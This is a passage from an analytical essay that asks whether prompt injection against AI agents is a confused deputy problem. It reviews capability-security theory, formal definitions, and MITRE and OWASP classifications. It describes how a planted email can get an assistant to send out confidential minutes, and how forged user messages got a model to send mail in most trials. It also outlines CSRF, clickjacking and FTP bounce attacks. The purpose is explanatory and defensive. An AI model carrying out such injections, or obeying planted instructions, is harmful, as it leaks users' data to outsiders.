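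This shows that there is no guarantee, but it doesn't show that some attack must succeed. In Pant and colleagues' own small test, two models refused all five attacks. The property they prove unattainable is that a model's decisions about things like tool use stay the same when someone rewords untrusted text without changing its meaning. This is not quite immunity to injection, because a model that obeyed every injection, however the attacker worded it, would also have this property.

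More importantly for the inference, the theorem excludes systems in which something outside the model decides whether a tool call runs. The domain list in *Silent Egress* was such a system, and it worked even though the model tried to leak the key every time. Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent, which checks tool calls against rules, and found that it cut the attack success rate from 25.8 to 4.2 percent. An attack they wrote with the defence in mind succeeded 2.6 percent of the time, though this was a single template against a weak model. Some other designs fix the agent's plan before the agent reads anything untrusted. David C also recommends safeguards outside the model, so "can't be mitigated" makes sense only as a claim about the model's confusion, not about the resulting harm.

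External safeguards also have limits. In *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026) reject the diagnosis that prompt injection comes from mixing instructions with data. Their example is an email that requests a travel refund and falsely states that the department head has approved it. That statement causes the harm, even though it isn't an instruction. A system that stops the agent from relying on such statements will also make it ignore genuine approvals.

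In their formal argument, they compare two situations that look identical to the agent, one with a real approval and one with a forgery. The agent must therefore act with the same probability *p* in both. The attack succeeds with probability *p*, and the legitimate request fails with probability 1 − *p*, so reducing one raises the other. Better verification can ease this trade-off by giving the agent evidence that distinguishes the two situations, such as a signed approval, a company record or an answer from the user. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian accept that the theorem does not show that such indistinguishable pairs will always exist, since that depends on what a particular system can verify.

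A forged approval can also replace a task. In one experiment, the user had not authorised an email assistant running on Claude Sonnet 4.6 to send anything. Fixed emails got it to send a message less than 1 percent of the time. A second copy of the same model, rewriting the emails over repeated attempts, succeeded in 96.7 percent of 150 scenarios, most often by inventing an earlier message from the user. The attacking copy had the assistant's system prompt and feedback on each attempt, which a supplier would rarely have. The forgery also worked only because nothing checked whether the user had sent that message, which a mail server could do.

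### Reliable systems from unreliable parts

The security writer Bruce Schneier and Barath Raghavan make a related argument in *Agentic AI's OODA Loop Problem* (2025). They write that no mechanism exists to mark the privileges of tokens, and that attackers can imitate each proposed substitute, for example by including delimiters when developers use them. They say that "we can't build reliable systems on unreliable foundations", and that prompt injection "might be unsolvable in today's LLMs".

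Their next essay, *Why AI Keeps Falling for Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026), calls the problem unsolvable, then says that nobody knows whether an immune model is possible. It suggests keeping agents narrow. A drive-through restaurant's agent, for example, would handle food orders and refer everything else to a manager. *The Promptware Kill Chain* (February 2026), by Schneier, Brodt and colleagues, describes injection as the first step of a longer attack whose later steps defenders can interrupt.

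*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues instead that secure systems can be built from untrusted components, as security engineers have long done. An operating system, for example, has to withstand hostile programs. A reader of Schneier and Raghavan's first essay similarly objected that we rely on shops and hospitals even though fallible people run them.

I think the disagreement is mostly about which property has to be reliable. A correct domain list can keep a key off the attacker's server even if the attacker controls everything the model does, because the protection doesn't depend on the model. But it can't ensure that the model summarizes a hostile page accurately. The system around the model also has to be sound. In the OpenAI incident, the network restrictions were outside the model, but the package service acted as a confused deputy of the kind Hardy described, making external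 requests for the agents that they could not make directly.

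## The view that it is a different failure: the deputy has been taken over

In the OpenAI incident, the package service kept doing its own job, fetching software, and the agents only chose what it fetched. The assistant in case B takes on a new job that the supplier wrote. On a third view, the assistant is therefore a hijacked program and not a confused deputy, and using one name for both leads engineers to choose the wrong fix.

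### A definition built on naming a resource

In *Gemini discusses Confused Deputy* (2026), Miller posted answers from Google's Gemini model to a mailing list of capability specialists, who corrected the answers. Alan Karp defined a confused deputy as one that "uses its permissions on a resource designated by someone else," a definition he finds most people understand.

Taken literally, this covers too much, since it also fits a web server that reads whichever public page a visitor names. Jonathan Shapiro added a second step, in which the deputy "has no way to associate the specific permissions it intends to use" with the resource. Tymshare's compiler had this problem because it could not ask to open the debugging file under the user's authority alone. Karp objected that some certificate systems do let a deputy tie a permission to a resource. He conceded the point after Miller answered that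 those are capability systems, or close to it, and that Shapiro meant systems without capabilities.

Karp also listed parts of Gemini's answer that match mistakes he has heard from other people, many of them working on the safety of AI agents. The list mixes supposed examples with supposed remedies:

- *Cloud services.* Gemini's example was a service that reaches into another customer's account because an access policy is too permissive. Karp blames systems in which a service can act for someone only by impersonating them.
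- *Administrator scripts.* A user passes malicious parameters to a script that runs with an administrator's privileges. Karp replies that the confused deputy has nothing to do with badly cleaned input.
- *Least privilege.* Giving a program only the permissions it needs "solves other problems".
- *Checking whom the deputy acts for.* The part of the compiler that writes the log acts for the compiler and not for the requester.
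- *Input validation.* The deputy would have to know what each requester may do, and giving it that knowledge can break company policy or medical privacy law.

Karp finds that most of these rest on the belief that a bug makes the deputy open the wrong resource, but Hardy's compiler had no such bug.

Gemini's answer also included AI agents among the examples, and Karp did not comment on that item. He was more direct four months later in *Confused deputy* (Karp, 2026). When the programmer Douglas Crockford imagined an attacker who asks a deputy for its private key and gets it, Karp replied that this is not a confused deputy vulnerability and repeated his definition. Miller added that the attack, "despite the name, has nothing to do with confusing the deputy." A planted email does confuse an agent in the everyday sense, which may be one reason people use the old name.

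Karp also edits a draft for the Decentralized Identity Foundation by Bucci, Caballero and colleagues. *Delegated Authority Problem Space Report* discusses the two problems separately. It traces the confused deputy to the separation of designation from permission. The remedy is for a program with a broad permission to narrow it to the one resource it wants before making a request. The draft discusses clever prompts under the keeping of secrets, because an agent might give away its key to anyone who asks in the right way. For that problem Karp proposes an "Agent Policy Enforcer", an ordinary program that keeps the secrets, uses them for the agent, and can block dangerous requests.

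### Who designates the board minutes

Case A meets Karp's definition because the supplier names a file and the assistant opens it with permissions that the supplier lacks. The test Karp proposed in *Testing for a confused deputy vulnerability* (2019) gives the same result. In the test, Alice calls Bob's service and names Carol's service in the call. The system is vulnerable if Bob can't then use Carol's service with Alice's permissions. In Case A, the supplier is Alice, the assistant is Bob's service and the company's file store is Carol's. The assistant can't open the file with the supplier's permissions, so the system is vulnerable.

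The remaining doubt about case A is that the supplier never called the assistant. The same doubt divided members of the mailing list in 2025 over Karp's example of a service that tells Alice which of her own files to update. Gernot Heiser, an operating-systems researcher, called the service's owner a "malicious trustee" to whom Alice had in effect given control of her data. Karp replied that the owner could not write to the files. Raoul Duke said a deputy has to be someone other than oneself, so Alice had nobody else to blame. But Mike Stay saw Alice as the deputy because she was acting on strings someone else supplied.

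Karp argued that the name should stay because the same fix works. Alice gives the service a capability for each file it may choose, and the service returns one of them. The office worker could similarly let the supplier pick from a set of purchasing documents. That seems a good reason to group case A with Hardy's compiler, regardless of which party called the other.

Case B is harder to classify. If the hidden passage contains the file name, someone else has designated the resource, which literally satisfies the definition. If the passage only describes the minutes, the assistant searches for them and picks the file. A precise description could count as a designation, since "the minutes of the last board meeting" singles out one document. But the attacker could as easily ask for whatever would most embarrass the company, and then the assistant would choose the document. Karp's reply to Crockford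 suggests that he would not count even a precise description as a designation, because "your private key" also singles out one thing. But he may have meant only that giving a key away is different from using a permission on it.

Shapiro's addition separates the cases more clearly. Suppose the assistant could state whose permission it is using for every file it opens. In case A that would help, because the assistant could ask for the file under a permission limited to what suppliers may see. In case B it would correctly state that it was using the office worker's permission to open the office worker's file, and then still mail the minutes to the supplier. Karp also calls the old problem "rights confusion", meaning confusion about whose rights to use, but the assistant in case B knows whose rights it is using and is carrying out the wrong task.

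Rajani, Garg and Rezk tie the term less closely to naming a resource. Their paper, *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, gives a broader formal definition and relates it to the integrity of information flow.

### The companion problem

Hardy calls Trojan horses "the companion problem" to the confused deputy. A Trojan horse is a program that does something useful while secretly exploiting the authority of the user who runs it. If the compiler's author had been malicious, the compiler could have translated a customer's program as usual and also copied the customer's private files to the author's directory. The operating system would have allowed this because the customer was entitled to read those files and had started the compiler.

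| | Hardy's compiler | Trojan horse | Case A | Case B |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Who started the program | The user who named the billing file | The victim | The office worker | The office worker |
| Who made the harmful kind of step part of the task | Tymshare's programmers | The attacker | The office worker | The supplier |
| Who chose the file | The user | The attacker | The supplier | The supplier or the assistant |
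| Whose authority opened it | Tymshare's | The victim's | The office worker's | The office worker's |

Case B matches the Trojan horse in almost every respect. The assistant runs a procedure that the attacker wrote, using the authority of the person who started the assistant. In Case A, an honest party set the task, as at Tymshare, but the authority came from the person who started the program, as with a Trojan horse.

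The comparison also explains why least privilege works differently in the two problems. If the compiler's license had covered only the statistics file, that file would still have been exposed, so Karp has reason to say that least privilege solves other problems. The Trojan horse is one of them, because a malicious compiler that can open only the source and output files has nothing else to steal. The same is true of an assistant in case B that can read only the one email. Case A still needs the limit that the office worker did not state.

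"Trojan horse" describes the assistant's position after the attack has worked, but not how the attacker got in. The usual defences against a Trojan horse examine the program before anyone runs it, for instance by checking who published it. The office worker's assistant would pass, because neither its code nor its model is malicious. The hostile instructions arrive later, in an email that the worker had good reason to want summarised. In this respect the attack is more like SQL injection, which also works on a legitimate program.

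The hijack may also fail or stop halfway. A processor carries out a Trojan horse's instructions every time, whereas most of the models that Ye and colleagues tested nearly always ignored the fake user command. An assistant might open the minutes and then decline to send them. Like a Trojan horse, the assistant also does its advertised job, which here is writing the summary. But a Trojan horse remains malicious until someone deletes it, while the same assistant may handle the next email correctly in a fresh session.

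It makes sense to assume a complete takeover when deciding how much authority to give an agent, as David C recommends, but that assumption is a poor estimate of what a given email will do. Confused deputies and Trojan horses also don't necessarily need separate systems, even if they are different kinds of problem. Hardy blamed the same access-list design for both, and said his company's capability system, KeyKOS, had facilities to aid deputies and to defeat Trojan horses.

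### Separate conditions in a formal framework

Siu, He and colleagues, in *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026), give the two failures separate formal conditions. Their starting point is that the same action can be legitimate or a breach depending on who asked for it and why. Deleting a file may be routine cleanup or sabotage. Their conditions use four ingredients:

- *R* is the set of permissions. The pair (*x*, *y*) is in *R* if *x* may access or influence *y*.
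- *S* is the set of authenticated sources, such as a logged-in user. Web pages and incoming emails are outside it.
- *Hₐ* equals 1 if an action serves the objective of the user's request, given the agent's earlier steps, and 0 if it does not.
- *Hₜ* is the same judgement applied to the agent's whole course of action.

A confused deputy attack occurs when an authenticated user gets the agent to access a target for which

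(user, target) ∉ *R*, but (agent, target) ∈ *R*

In their example, an employee asks an agent to show all salaries. The employee has no access to the personnel database, but the agent has access for administrative work and shows the salaries. The agent should have used the employee's permissions instead of its own.

Indirect prompt injection requires two things at once. An instruction behind the action came from some source *s*, and

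*s* ∉ *S* and *Hₐ* = 0

An agent meets both conditions if, while summarising customer emails, it obeys one that tells it to send all the customer data to a stranger. A cooking assistant that follows a recipe website's instruction to bake at 350°F meets only the first, because baking serves the user's request. Siu and colleagues call it task drift when an agent changes course without authorisation but *Hₜ* = 0. For example, their cooking assistant drifts without any attacker when it is told to buy ingredients and starts shopping for a skillet.

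Under these conditions, neither case A nor case B is a confused deputy attack, because the office worker may read the minutes. Case B is an injection, because mailing the minutes does not help produce a summary. Case A is not an injection, because the worker's request was to mail the document that the supplier asked for, so *Hₐ* equals 1. If someone has recorded that the minutes may not go to suppliers, case A does break another rule in the framework, which allows information to pass only between parties that *R* connects.

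Siu and colleagues separate the failures by what the user is allowed to do, which is a different boundary from Karp's. Case A meets his definition but not theirs. The salary request meets both, although the employee supplied the agent's entire task and not just the name of a database. Their boundary is therefore also different from the one between an attacker who controls an argument and one who controls the task.

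In another of their examples, a user tells the cooking assistant to order ingredients for dinner, and the recipe page contains the words "use payment method ending in 9876". The assistant pays with that card. It is still ordering dinner, and paying serves the order, so *Hₜ* and *Hₐ* are both 1 and there is no injection under their conditions. The user is allowed to use the card, so there is no confused deputy either. But an outsider has chosen which of the user's resources the agent uses, which very nearly meets Karp's definition.

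Siu and colleagues do regard this as a breach of what they call source authorization, because only the user should choose the card. But their combined formula for a secure action accepts an instruction from an unauthenticated source whenever *Hₐ* = 1. They included that exception so that agents could follow recipes, but as written it also allows the payment. One could fix this by judging *Hₐ* more finely, so that paying with a card the user did not choose scores 0. The payment would then count as an injection, and so might case A, depending on how strictly someone read the worker's request, so the framework does not settle how to classify argument control.

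The two failures can also occur in sequence. In another example, a malicious document contains the false claim that Alice has temporary administrator rights to every database, and an agent stores this claim in its long-term memory. When Alice later asks for data, the agent retrieves the claim and gives her access she isn't entitled to. The planted text makes the agent a confused deputy for Alice without replacing her task, and she may not know the document exists.

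*Hₐ*, *Hₜ* and the function that traces an action to the instruction behind it are ideals, and Siu and colleagues accept that real systems can only approximate them. They call the tracing an open problem in interpretability, the study of what happens inside a model. To support their emphasis on *Hₐ*, they cite results from AgentDojo. Restricting the agent's tools cut successful attacks by 88 percent and a detector for injected text cut them by 86 percent, while marking off untrusted text or repeating the user's prompt cut them by at most 28 percent. They describe the first two defenses as checking consistency with the task. That description fits restricting tools, but a detector inspects incoming text. This detector also lowered the share of tasks the agent completed when there was no attack, from 69.0 to 41.5 percent.

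### How MITRE and OWASP file the two problems

How a weakness is classified has practical effects, because engineers often look it up in a public catalogue and apply the remedies listed there. MITRE, an American nonprofit, maintains the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), a numbered list of flaws in software and hardware. The confused deputy is entry 441, and GCVE's *Unintended Proxy or Intermediary ('Confused Deputy')* reproduces the entry in full. The flaw is that a product passes on a request without preserving its original source, so the request seems to come from the product.

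In the entry's example, a chip blocks a microcontroller from reading registers that hold secrets. The microcontroller directs another component, which moves data in memory, to copy the registers to a location the microcontroller can read. The copy succeeds because the second component makes the request under its own identity. MITRE's remedy is to pass the original requester's identity on to the target, which can then refuse the request.

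In case B, it is unclear who the original requester is. If it is the office worker who started the assistant, both the file store and the mail server will accept the request. If it is the supplier, the tool call has to be traced back to the supplier's sentence, and Siu and colleagues call such tracing an open problem.

MITRE's *CWE-1427*, the entry for prompt injection, classifies it as a kind of command injection. The remedies concern what goes into the model. MITRE gives its highest effectiveness rating to cleaning the input, and a moderate one to building prompts that separate user input from the developer's instructions. In the first example, a chatbot explains the difference between two numbered CWE entries. An attacker adds a request for a pirate poem about a parrot to one of the numbers, and the program stops this by accepting only text in the form of a CWE number.

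That fix is complete, but it depends on an input with a fixed form. A supplier's email has no fixed form, so case B has no comparable fix. The high rating is also hard to reconcile with David C's view that a model enforces no boundary between instructions and content. MITRE partly allows for this by warning, in a note in the entry, that indirect prompt injection may have a different root cause and need a different number, though it does not name one.

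However, MITRE notes in its confused deputy entry that one could argue the confused deputy is part of most vulnerabilities that need an active attacker, including SQL injection, because the vulnerable program already has the authority that the attacker misuses. That is true, and it is also a reason to be careful about using the term broadly. A label that fits SQL injection, the compiler and case B equally well doesn't help an engineer choose between parameterised queries, capabilities and a smaller set of tools.

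OWASP (2025) worked with more than 100 specialists to draw up a separate list of the ten main risks for AI agents. TechRepublic's *OWASP Drops First AI Agent Risk List* summarises the first entry, Agent Goal Hijack, as malicious content that alters an agent's objectives or decision path. The third, Identity and Privilege Abuse, covers agents that reuse, escalate or leak credentials they have inherited. PointGuard AI's *OWASP ASI03* places the confused deputy under this third entry, as a low-privilege agent that relays valid-looking instructions to a more privileged one. This differs considerably from the case of Hardy's compiler, because one agent passes the other whole instructions and not just a file name.

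Writers do not apply the categories consistently. An article in SC Media retells Hardy's story and then assigns this class of attack to Agent Goal Hijack. Case B belongs there. Case A, which is closer to the compiler case, fits neither Agent Goal Hijack nor the entry on misused credentials well, because the supplier does not change the agent's objective and nobody misuses a credential. The entry on agents that misuse legitimate tools because of ambiguous prompts, excess privilege or poisoned inputs suits it better.

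The remedies for goal hijacking and privilege abuse overlap more than the categories themselves. For goal hijacking, the security company Zealynx recommends ranking instructions by source, cleaning content, limiting the authority of tools and asking a person to approve high-stakes actions. For privilege abuse, Aikido, another security company, lists short-lived credentials, a separate identity for each agent, permissions limited to the task and an authorization check on every action. Both lists include limits on what the agent can do, and these are the measures most likely to protect the board minutes in case B. Short-lived credentials would help little in that case because the assistant sends the minutes within seconds of reading the email, while its credentials are still valid.

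## What earlier attackers could control, and what capabilities are proved to stop

Karp's definition of a confused deputy covers an attacker who designates a resource, but security researchers have long applied the term to attacks in which the outsider supplies more than a file name. In 2016, Rajani and colleagues gave a formal definition that does not mention naming, and they list cross-site request forgery, clickjacking and the FTP bounce attack as common examples. The broader usage matters because if the theory covered only designation, task replacement would fall outside it, and there would be no particular reason to expect its remedies to work.

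### Requests that the user never made

When someone logs in to a website, the site gives their browser a cookie, a small piece of data that the browser includes in every later request to that site. The site treats requests with the cookie as the user's own. Browsers also let any web page send requests to any address. In cross-site request forgery, a malicious page sends a request to another site where the visitor is logged in, and the browser includes the visitor's cookie.

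Gmail had a cross-site request forgery (CSRF) flaw in late 2007, according to *Robust Defenses for Cross-Site Request Forgery* (Barth, Jackson and Mitchell, 2008). A malicious page could make a visitor's browser ask Gmail to create a filter that forwarded all the visitor's mail to the attacker. The paper names a victim who lost control of a web domain this way, but adds that this person later repudiated the incident. *Lightweight Server Support for Browser-Based CSRF Protection* (Czeskis, Moshchuk and colleagues) describes the cookie as ambient authority and the browser as a confused deputy.

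In the Gmail case, the attacker chose the site, the operation and every value in the request. The user had asked only to see a web page, not to create a mail filter. In this respect, request forgery is closer to case B than to case A.

Browser makers deliberately let pages send requests to other sites, whereas the developer of the assistant in case B never meant suppliers to choose its tool calls. This distinguishes the two better than whether the program's job changed, because that depends on how one describes the job. The browser's job stayed the same, since its programmers wrote it to send whatever requests a page contains. The assistant's job changed if it is described as summarising, since the assistant went on to search and send mail, but not if it is described as running whatever tool calls the model outputs.

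The term fits a variant called login request forgery even less well. The attacker's page logs the visitor in to a site with the attacker's own username and password. Barth and colleagues describe a dishonest merchant who does this on PayPal, so that a customer who then enters a credit card adds it to the merchant's account. The attacker uses nobody else's authority at the login, and the harm comes from what the customer does afterwards.

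In clickjacking, a malicious page loads another site's page in a transparent frame over something tempting, such as a game. When the user clicks on the game, the click lands on an invisible button that might start a webcam recording. Waterken's *The Confused Deputy rides again!* compares the browser to Hardy's compiler, because the browser works for both the user and the page and cannot specify which of them a request is for. The attacker supplies the framed page's address and screen position but relies on the user to click the hidden button unknowingly.

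The FTP bounce attack uses a File Transfer Protocol feature that lets a client tell a server to send a file to a third machine. *FTP Security Considerations* (Allman and Ostermann, 1999) explains that an attacker can upload a file of mail commands and have the server send it to another machine's mail service. The connection comes from the FTP server, so the attack can get around rules that restrict access by network address. The attacker names a destination, as Hardy's user did, but also supplies a short program of mail commands for the service to run.

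### From a file name to a goal

These attacks and the two imaginary emails can be put in order by what the attacker supplies.

| What the attacker supplies | Examples | Who works out the harmful steps | What limits the damage |
|---|---|---|---|
| A name | Hardy's compiler, case A | The deputy's programmers, who wrote them for another purpose | The few things the code does with a name |
| A request from a fixed menu | Request forgery | The website's programmers, who wrote them for another purpose | The operations the site offers |
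| A program in a fixed language | SQL injection, the mail commands in an FTP bounce | The attacker | What the language can express and the receiving service permits |
| A goal in ordinary language | Case B | The assistant | The assistant's tools and permissions |

This order shows that attackers were writing their own procedures for other people's programs long before language models. It does not rank the attacks by severity, since one forged bank transfer may cost more than a stolen table of data. Case B is new in that the supplier can leave the procedure to the assistant, and the input has no fixed grammar.

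Defenders can check commands that follow a fixed grammar. Allman and Ostermann suggest that FTP servers refuse to send files to ports below 1024, where the standard services listen. The rule leaves services on higher ports exposed, but a programmer can write it in one line.

The Gmail filter shows what happens to older defences when the attacker can supply a goal. The most popular defence against request forgery is a secret token, a hard-to-guess value that the site puts in its own forms. The site rejects any request without the token, and an attacker's page has no access to it. Waterken points out that this replaces ambient authority with explicit authority, because the sender must present something specific to the request.

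Barth and colleagues proposed another defence, a simple form of provenance tracking in which the browser adds a header identifying the site a request came from. An older header, Referer, already carried similar information, but networks often removed it for privacy. The researchers placed advertisements that caused 283,945 browsers to contact their servers, and found that Referer was usually still present on encrypted connections. A site that required Referer on those connections would have remained compatible with 99.9 percent of the users they observed.

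Now suppose an attacker plants text instructing a browsing agent to create the same filter. The agent can open Gmail's settings page, fill in the form and submit it. Both defences let the request through because the form contains the right token and the request comes from Gmail's page. They block requests from hostile pages, but here the agent uses the real page on the attacker's behalf.

### A definition without names

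Rajani and colleagues work with a very small programming language. Each memory location has an owner, and owners have ranks. Code runs with the authority of some principal and may write to a location only if that principal ranks at least as high as the location's owner. Each program has a gap that the attacker can fill with any code, which runs at a lower rank than the deputy's code.

The definition concerns the locations that an attacker might want to change. A program is free of confused deputy attacks if, whatever code the attacker puts in the gap, each of these locations meets at least one of two conditions when the program ends:

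1. *No control.* The location would have ended with the same value whatever code the attacker had used.
2. *Direct write.* The attacker, running alone, could have put that value there.

The attacker has achieved nothing if the first condition holds, and did not need a deputy if the second holds. The conditions do not depend on how the attacker's influence reached the location.

Hardy's compiler, without its statistics and billing, looks like this:

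```
# attacker's code
source := my_program
output := reference to BILL

# compiler's code
write compile(source) to the location in output
```

BILL fails both conditions. A different source program would have left different contents there, and the attacker has no authority to write to it.

In the paper's version of a capability system, the program stops whenever code computes a reference that it has no right to write through. The attacker's second line therefore fails, because the attacker cannot obtain a reference to BILL. The attacker can pass on references only to locations they could have written to directly, so the second condition holds, and Hardy's remedy provably works against this kind of attack.

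### What capabilities miss

In the next example, which Rajani and colleagues call a value attack, the deputy's own code determines where the write goes:

```
# attacker's code
request := 42

# deputy's code
record := request
```

The attacker may write to `request` but not to `record`. The final value of `record` still depends on the attacker, so this is a confused deputy attack under the definition. Capabilities do not stop it, because the attacker never handles a reference to `record`. Rajani and colleagues compare it to SQL injection, with the web server as the deputy. Karp would presumably not call it a confused deputy attack, because he says that badly cleaned input has nothing to do with confused deputies.

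In the implicit-influence example, the deputy does not even copy a value from the attacker:

```
# attacker's code
flag := true

# deputy's code
if flag then record := 41
else record := 42
```

Both numbers come from the deputy's code, but the attacker decides which one it writes.

Another attack uses a reference that was in memory from the start. The deputy follows the reference to a protected location and writes a value the attacker supplied.

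In the compiler example, the attacker gives the deputy the reference to the protected location. Rajani and colleagues call this *explicit designation*. In the other examples, the deputy already has the reference, and the attacker influences what the deputy writes through it. They call this *implicit designation*. In general, capabilities stop only explicit designation, because they control who can obtain a reference but don't limit what may influence its rightful holder.

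By Theorem 4 in the paper, capabilities are enough if the deputy's code contains no reference to a targeted location that the attacker cannot write to, and no such reference is in memory at the start. Code that a programmer has endorsed is exempt. The deputy could then get a dangerous reference only from the attacker, who can't obtain one either. Rajani and colleagues say that these restrictions make the language useless for almost all practical purposes. People use deputies because they have authority that their clients lack, and an assistant that met the conditions would have no authority over anything worth protecting from whoever supplies its task.

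Rajani and colleagues present this as a surprise, because earlier writers seemed to suggest that capabilities rule out confused deputies altogether. In *Capability Myths Demolished*, Miller and colleagues make a narrower claim. They define a confused deputy broadly, as one that someone has manipulated into "wielding its authority inappropriately", and case B fits that definition. But the type they say "simply cannot occur" is the common one, in which a malicious party designates a resource they are not supposed to access. They add that no security model can prevent people from writing bad programs.

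Tyler Close's *ACLs Don't* (2009) argues against the main alternative to capabilities, access control lists, which record who may use each resource. According to Close, these lists cannot produce correct access decisions when there are more than two principals, because messages between the principals do not retain the necessary information. Request forgery and clickjacking both exploit this flaw.

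Close said, in a discussion of a browser standard for messages between sites, that a program creates a confused deputy vulnerability when it takes an identifier from one party's response and puts it in a request to another. The assistant in case A does this with the file name in the supplier's email. Close's remedy is a web address containing an unguessable secret, so that anyone who supplies the address also supplies the authority to use it. This would help in case A, because the supplier does not know the secret address of the board minutes, but not in case B if the assistant could look up the address itself.

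### Tracking who influenced what

The simpler of Rajani and colleagues' two provenance-tracking systems labels each value with a rank no higher than that of any owner whose locations the program read to compute it. The system refuses to write a value to a protected location if the value's label is too low. This stops the value attack, because `request` belongs to the attacker, but it does not stop the implicit-influence attack, because 41 and 42 are constants in the deputy's code.

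Full tracking also labels the current point in the program. When the program enters an `if` or a loop, this label drops to the rank of the condition, and it returns to its earlier rank when the program leaves. Since `flag` belongs to the attacker, everything inside the `if` has the attacker's rank, and neither branch may write to `record`. Full tracking prevents every confused deputy attack in the language, apart from any influence that a programmer has deliberately endorsed (Theorem 6). This holds for any program and any starting memory.

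| Attack | Ordinary permission checks | Capabilities | Tracking values only | Full tracking |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The attacker passes a reference | Miss it | Stop it | Stops it | Stops it |
| The attacker supplies a value | Miss it | Miss it | Stops it | Stops it |
| The attacker chooses a branch | Miss it | Miss it | Misses it | Stops it |
| The reference was already in memory | Miss it | Miss it | Stops it | Stops it |

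Full tracking also blocks harmless programs. If code copies a value from a low-ranked owner's location to a higher-ranked owner's, the system refuses the write even when an attacker couldn't exploit the program. It does so because full tracking enforces noninterference, a stronger property under which nothing of low rank may affect anything of higher rank. Capabilities are too strict in other cases. They halt a run in which the attacker's code computes a forbidden reference, even if the deputy only ever writes the number 1.

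### The two emails as programs

The small language has no secrets, and its rules cover only unwanted writing. But one can treat the office worker's outgoing mail as a protected location, since the supplier has no authority to send mail from the worker's account. Case A then becomes:

```
name := file name in the supplier's email
outbox := message to supplier with the contents of name
```

Case B has the model choose the action:

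```
action := model(worker's request, supplier's email)
if action is "summarise" then show the summary
if action is "send minutes" then
    outbox := message to supplier with the minutes
```

In both programs, the assistant already has the authority to open the files and send the message, so both are examples of implicit designation. Case A resembles the value attack because the supplier's file name determines the contents of the message. If the supplier had to provide a capability for the document instead, the designation would be explicit, and the supplier would have no capability for the minutes. Case B resembles the implicit-influence attack because the supplier's text determines which action the assistant takes. This attack doesn't require the supplier to provide a capability, so a capability system has nothing to refuse unless someone has already narrowed the assistant's permissions.

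Full tracking would stop both leaks but, like the rule that David C passes on, it would also block a harmless purchase order in case A. The definition also counts that order as a confused deputy attack, because the supplier influenced the outgoing mail and could not have sent it directly. The worker wanted the supplier to choose the document, but the definition doesn't take that into account.

The blocking would also spread further in an assistant than in the small language. Suppose the worker asks for a summary of the supplier's email and then for a calendar entry for a meeting with a manager:

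1. The request arrives, and the model's sequence has the worker's rank.
2. The assistant reads the email, and the sequence drops to the supplier's rank.
3. The model writes the summary from the whole sequence, so the summary has the supplier's rank. This does no harm if the assistant only displays it.
4. The model writes the calendar entry from the same sequence, so the entry also has the supplier's rank, and the tracking system refuses to save it.

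The system cannot safely assume that the email had nothing to do with the meeting, because text in the email could have changed the time or added a guest. In the small language, each value has its own label, and the label on the current point in the program returns to its earlier value when an `if` ends, but an assistant's sequence still contains the email after the summary is finished. CaMeL, a system built for language-model agents, can label data more finely because it keeps values in program variables outside the model.

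### Endorsement as a necessary exception

A program that acts on outside input needs some way to let that input count. Strict noninterference is too rigid for realistic programs, according to Askarov and Myers (2011), in *Attacker Control and Impact for Confidentiality and Integrity*, who study how endorsement can relax it. One of their examples is a service that must not release new data before a certain time:

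```
if request_time >= embargo_time then release new_data
else release old_data
```

The requester supplies `request_time` and can get the data early by giving a false time, so an untrusted value leads to a leak, as with the board minutes. Askarov and Myers suggest a policy in which the program endorses the time only after checking that it is in the past. The requester can still choose among past times, but can't use a future time to end the embargo early.

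Rajani and colleagues need endorsement for the compiler's bill because a customer who submits a longer program should get a larger bill, and so must be able to influence the billing file. They mark the billing code as endorsed and apply their definition only to stretches of the program without endorsed code. Their theorems therefore don't guarantee that the endorsed code sets sensible limits. If a developer endorsed the whole step in which the assistant reads an email and chooses an action, the guarantee would cover neither leak.

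For case A, the developer could limit the endorsement to documents in the purchasing folder. An assistant asked to "deal with this email" would need limits on the kinds of action, the recipients and the files, and those limits might be different for the next request.

Ren, Chen and colleagues (2026) similarly observe that functions that accept calls from untrusted code and then change trusted data are dangerous but necessary, since applications must be able to ask an operating system to do things. They treat a confused deputy attack as a mismatch between a value's expected type and its actual type. In their example, a currency-exchange program expects each customer to supply a function that makes the customer's payment. An attacker supplies the exchange's own payment function, so the exchange pays the attacker instead of collecting money.

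Ren and colleagues check each call when it is made. The exchange marks its call as made on behalf of untrusted input, and its payment function, which accepts only trusted calls, rejects it. They used the proof checker Lean to prove that, with their run-time checks in place, an attacker who lies about types can do no more than one who follows the rules. They mention the Model Context Protocol as one setting where trusted programs may receive values of the wrong type. But a planted email has the right type, because the assistant expected text from an outsider and received it. A label could still mark the text as untrusted, and the mail tool could reject any call that depended on it, but the calendar tool would then have to reject such calls too.

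### Permissions that follow causes

Gallo (2026), in *Full Provenance on the COSS Causal Axis*, rereads the four attacks from the small language as different paths from a cause to an effect. Each event in a run carries a set of permissions, which Gallo writes as *C*(*e*) for an event *e*. An ordinary step may keep or drop permissions but may not add any. When an event has several causes, it keeps only the permissions that all of them carry:

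*C*(*e*) ⊆ *C*(*p*₁) ∩ *C*(*p*₂) ∩ …

Under these rules, if a request leads to a protected action through ordinary steps, the action can use only permissions that the request carried. This holds whether the influence passed through a reference, a value, a branch or stored memory. Gallo defines a confused deputy as one that uses a permission the request lacked, so none can occur under these rules. Gallo does not claim to reprove Theorem 6, and the two definitions of a confused deputy differ.

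The proof is short because the premises do most of the work:

- The record of causes must include every route by which a request can lead to a protected action.
- No ordinary step may add permissions.
- A check must compare every protected action with the permissions that reach it.

In case B, the result depends on what counts as the request. If only the worker's message counts, the assistant used permissions that the message carried and was not a confused deputy. If the supplier's email also counts, the model's next output has two causes and keeps only the permissions that the worker and the supplier share. The assistant could then open neither the minutes nor a purchase order, as under the rule that David C passes on. Case A would therefore need what Gallo calls an explicit authorized relaxation, which serves as endorsement.

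Gallo's rule is looser than full tracking in that it allows an action influenced by someone of low rank if every cause of the action carries the necessary permission. For example, a colleague who also had permission to send out the minutes could get the assistant to send them by planting text in an email.

An earlier paper, Gallo's *Beyond Proof of Possession* (2026), explains why valid credentials are not enough. An agent may present the same key in two write requests, yet what led to each request may make one acceptable and the other unacceptable. Similarly, the assistant's credentials are equally valid when it sends a purchase order and when it leaks the minutes. But it is hard to establish what led to a language model's action, because every text in the sequence can affect every output. A complete record would therefore list all the texts as causes of each action, and a shorter one would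 require the tracing that Siu and colleagues call an open problem.

### What a fixed program leaves out

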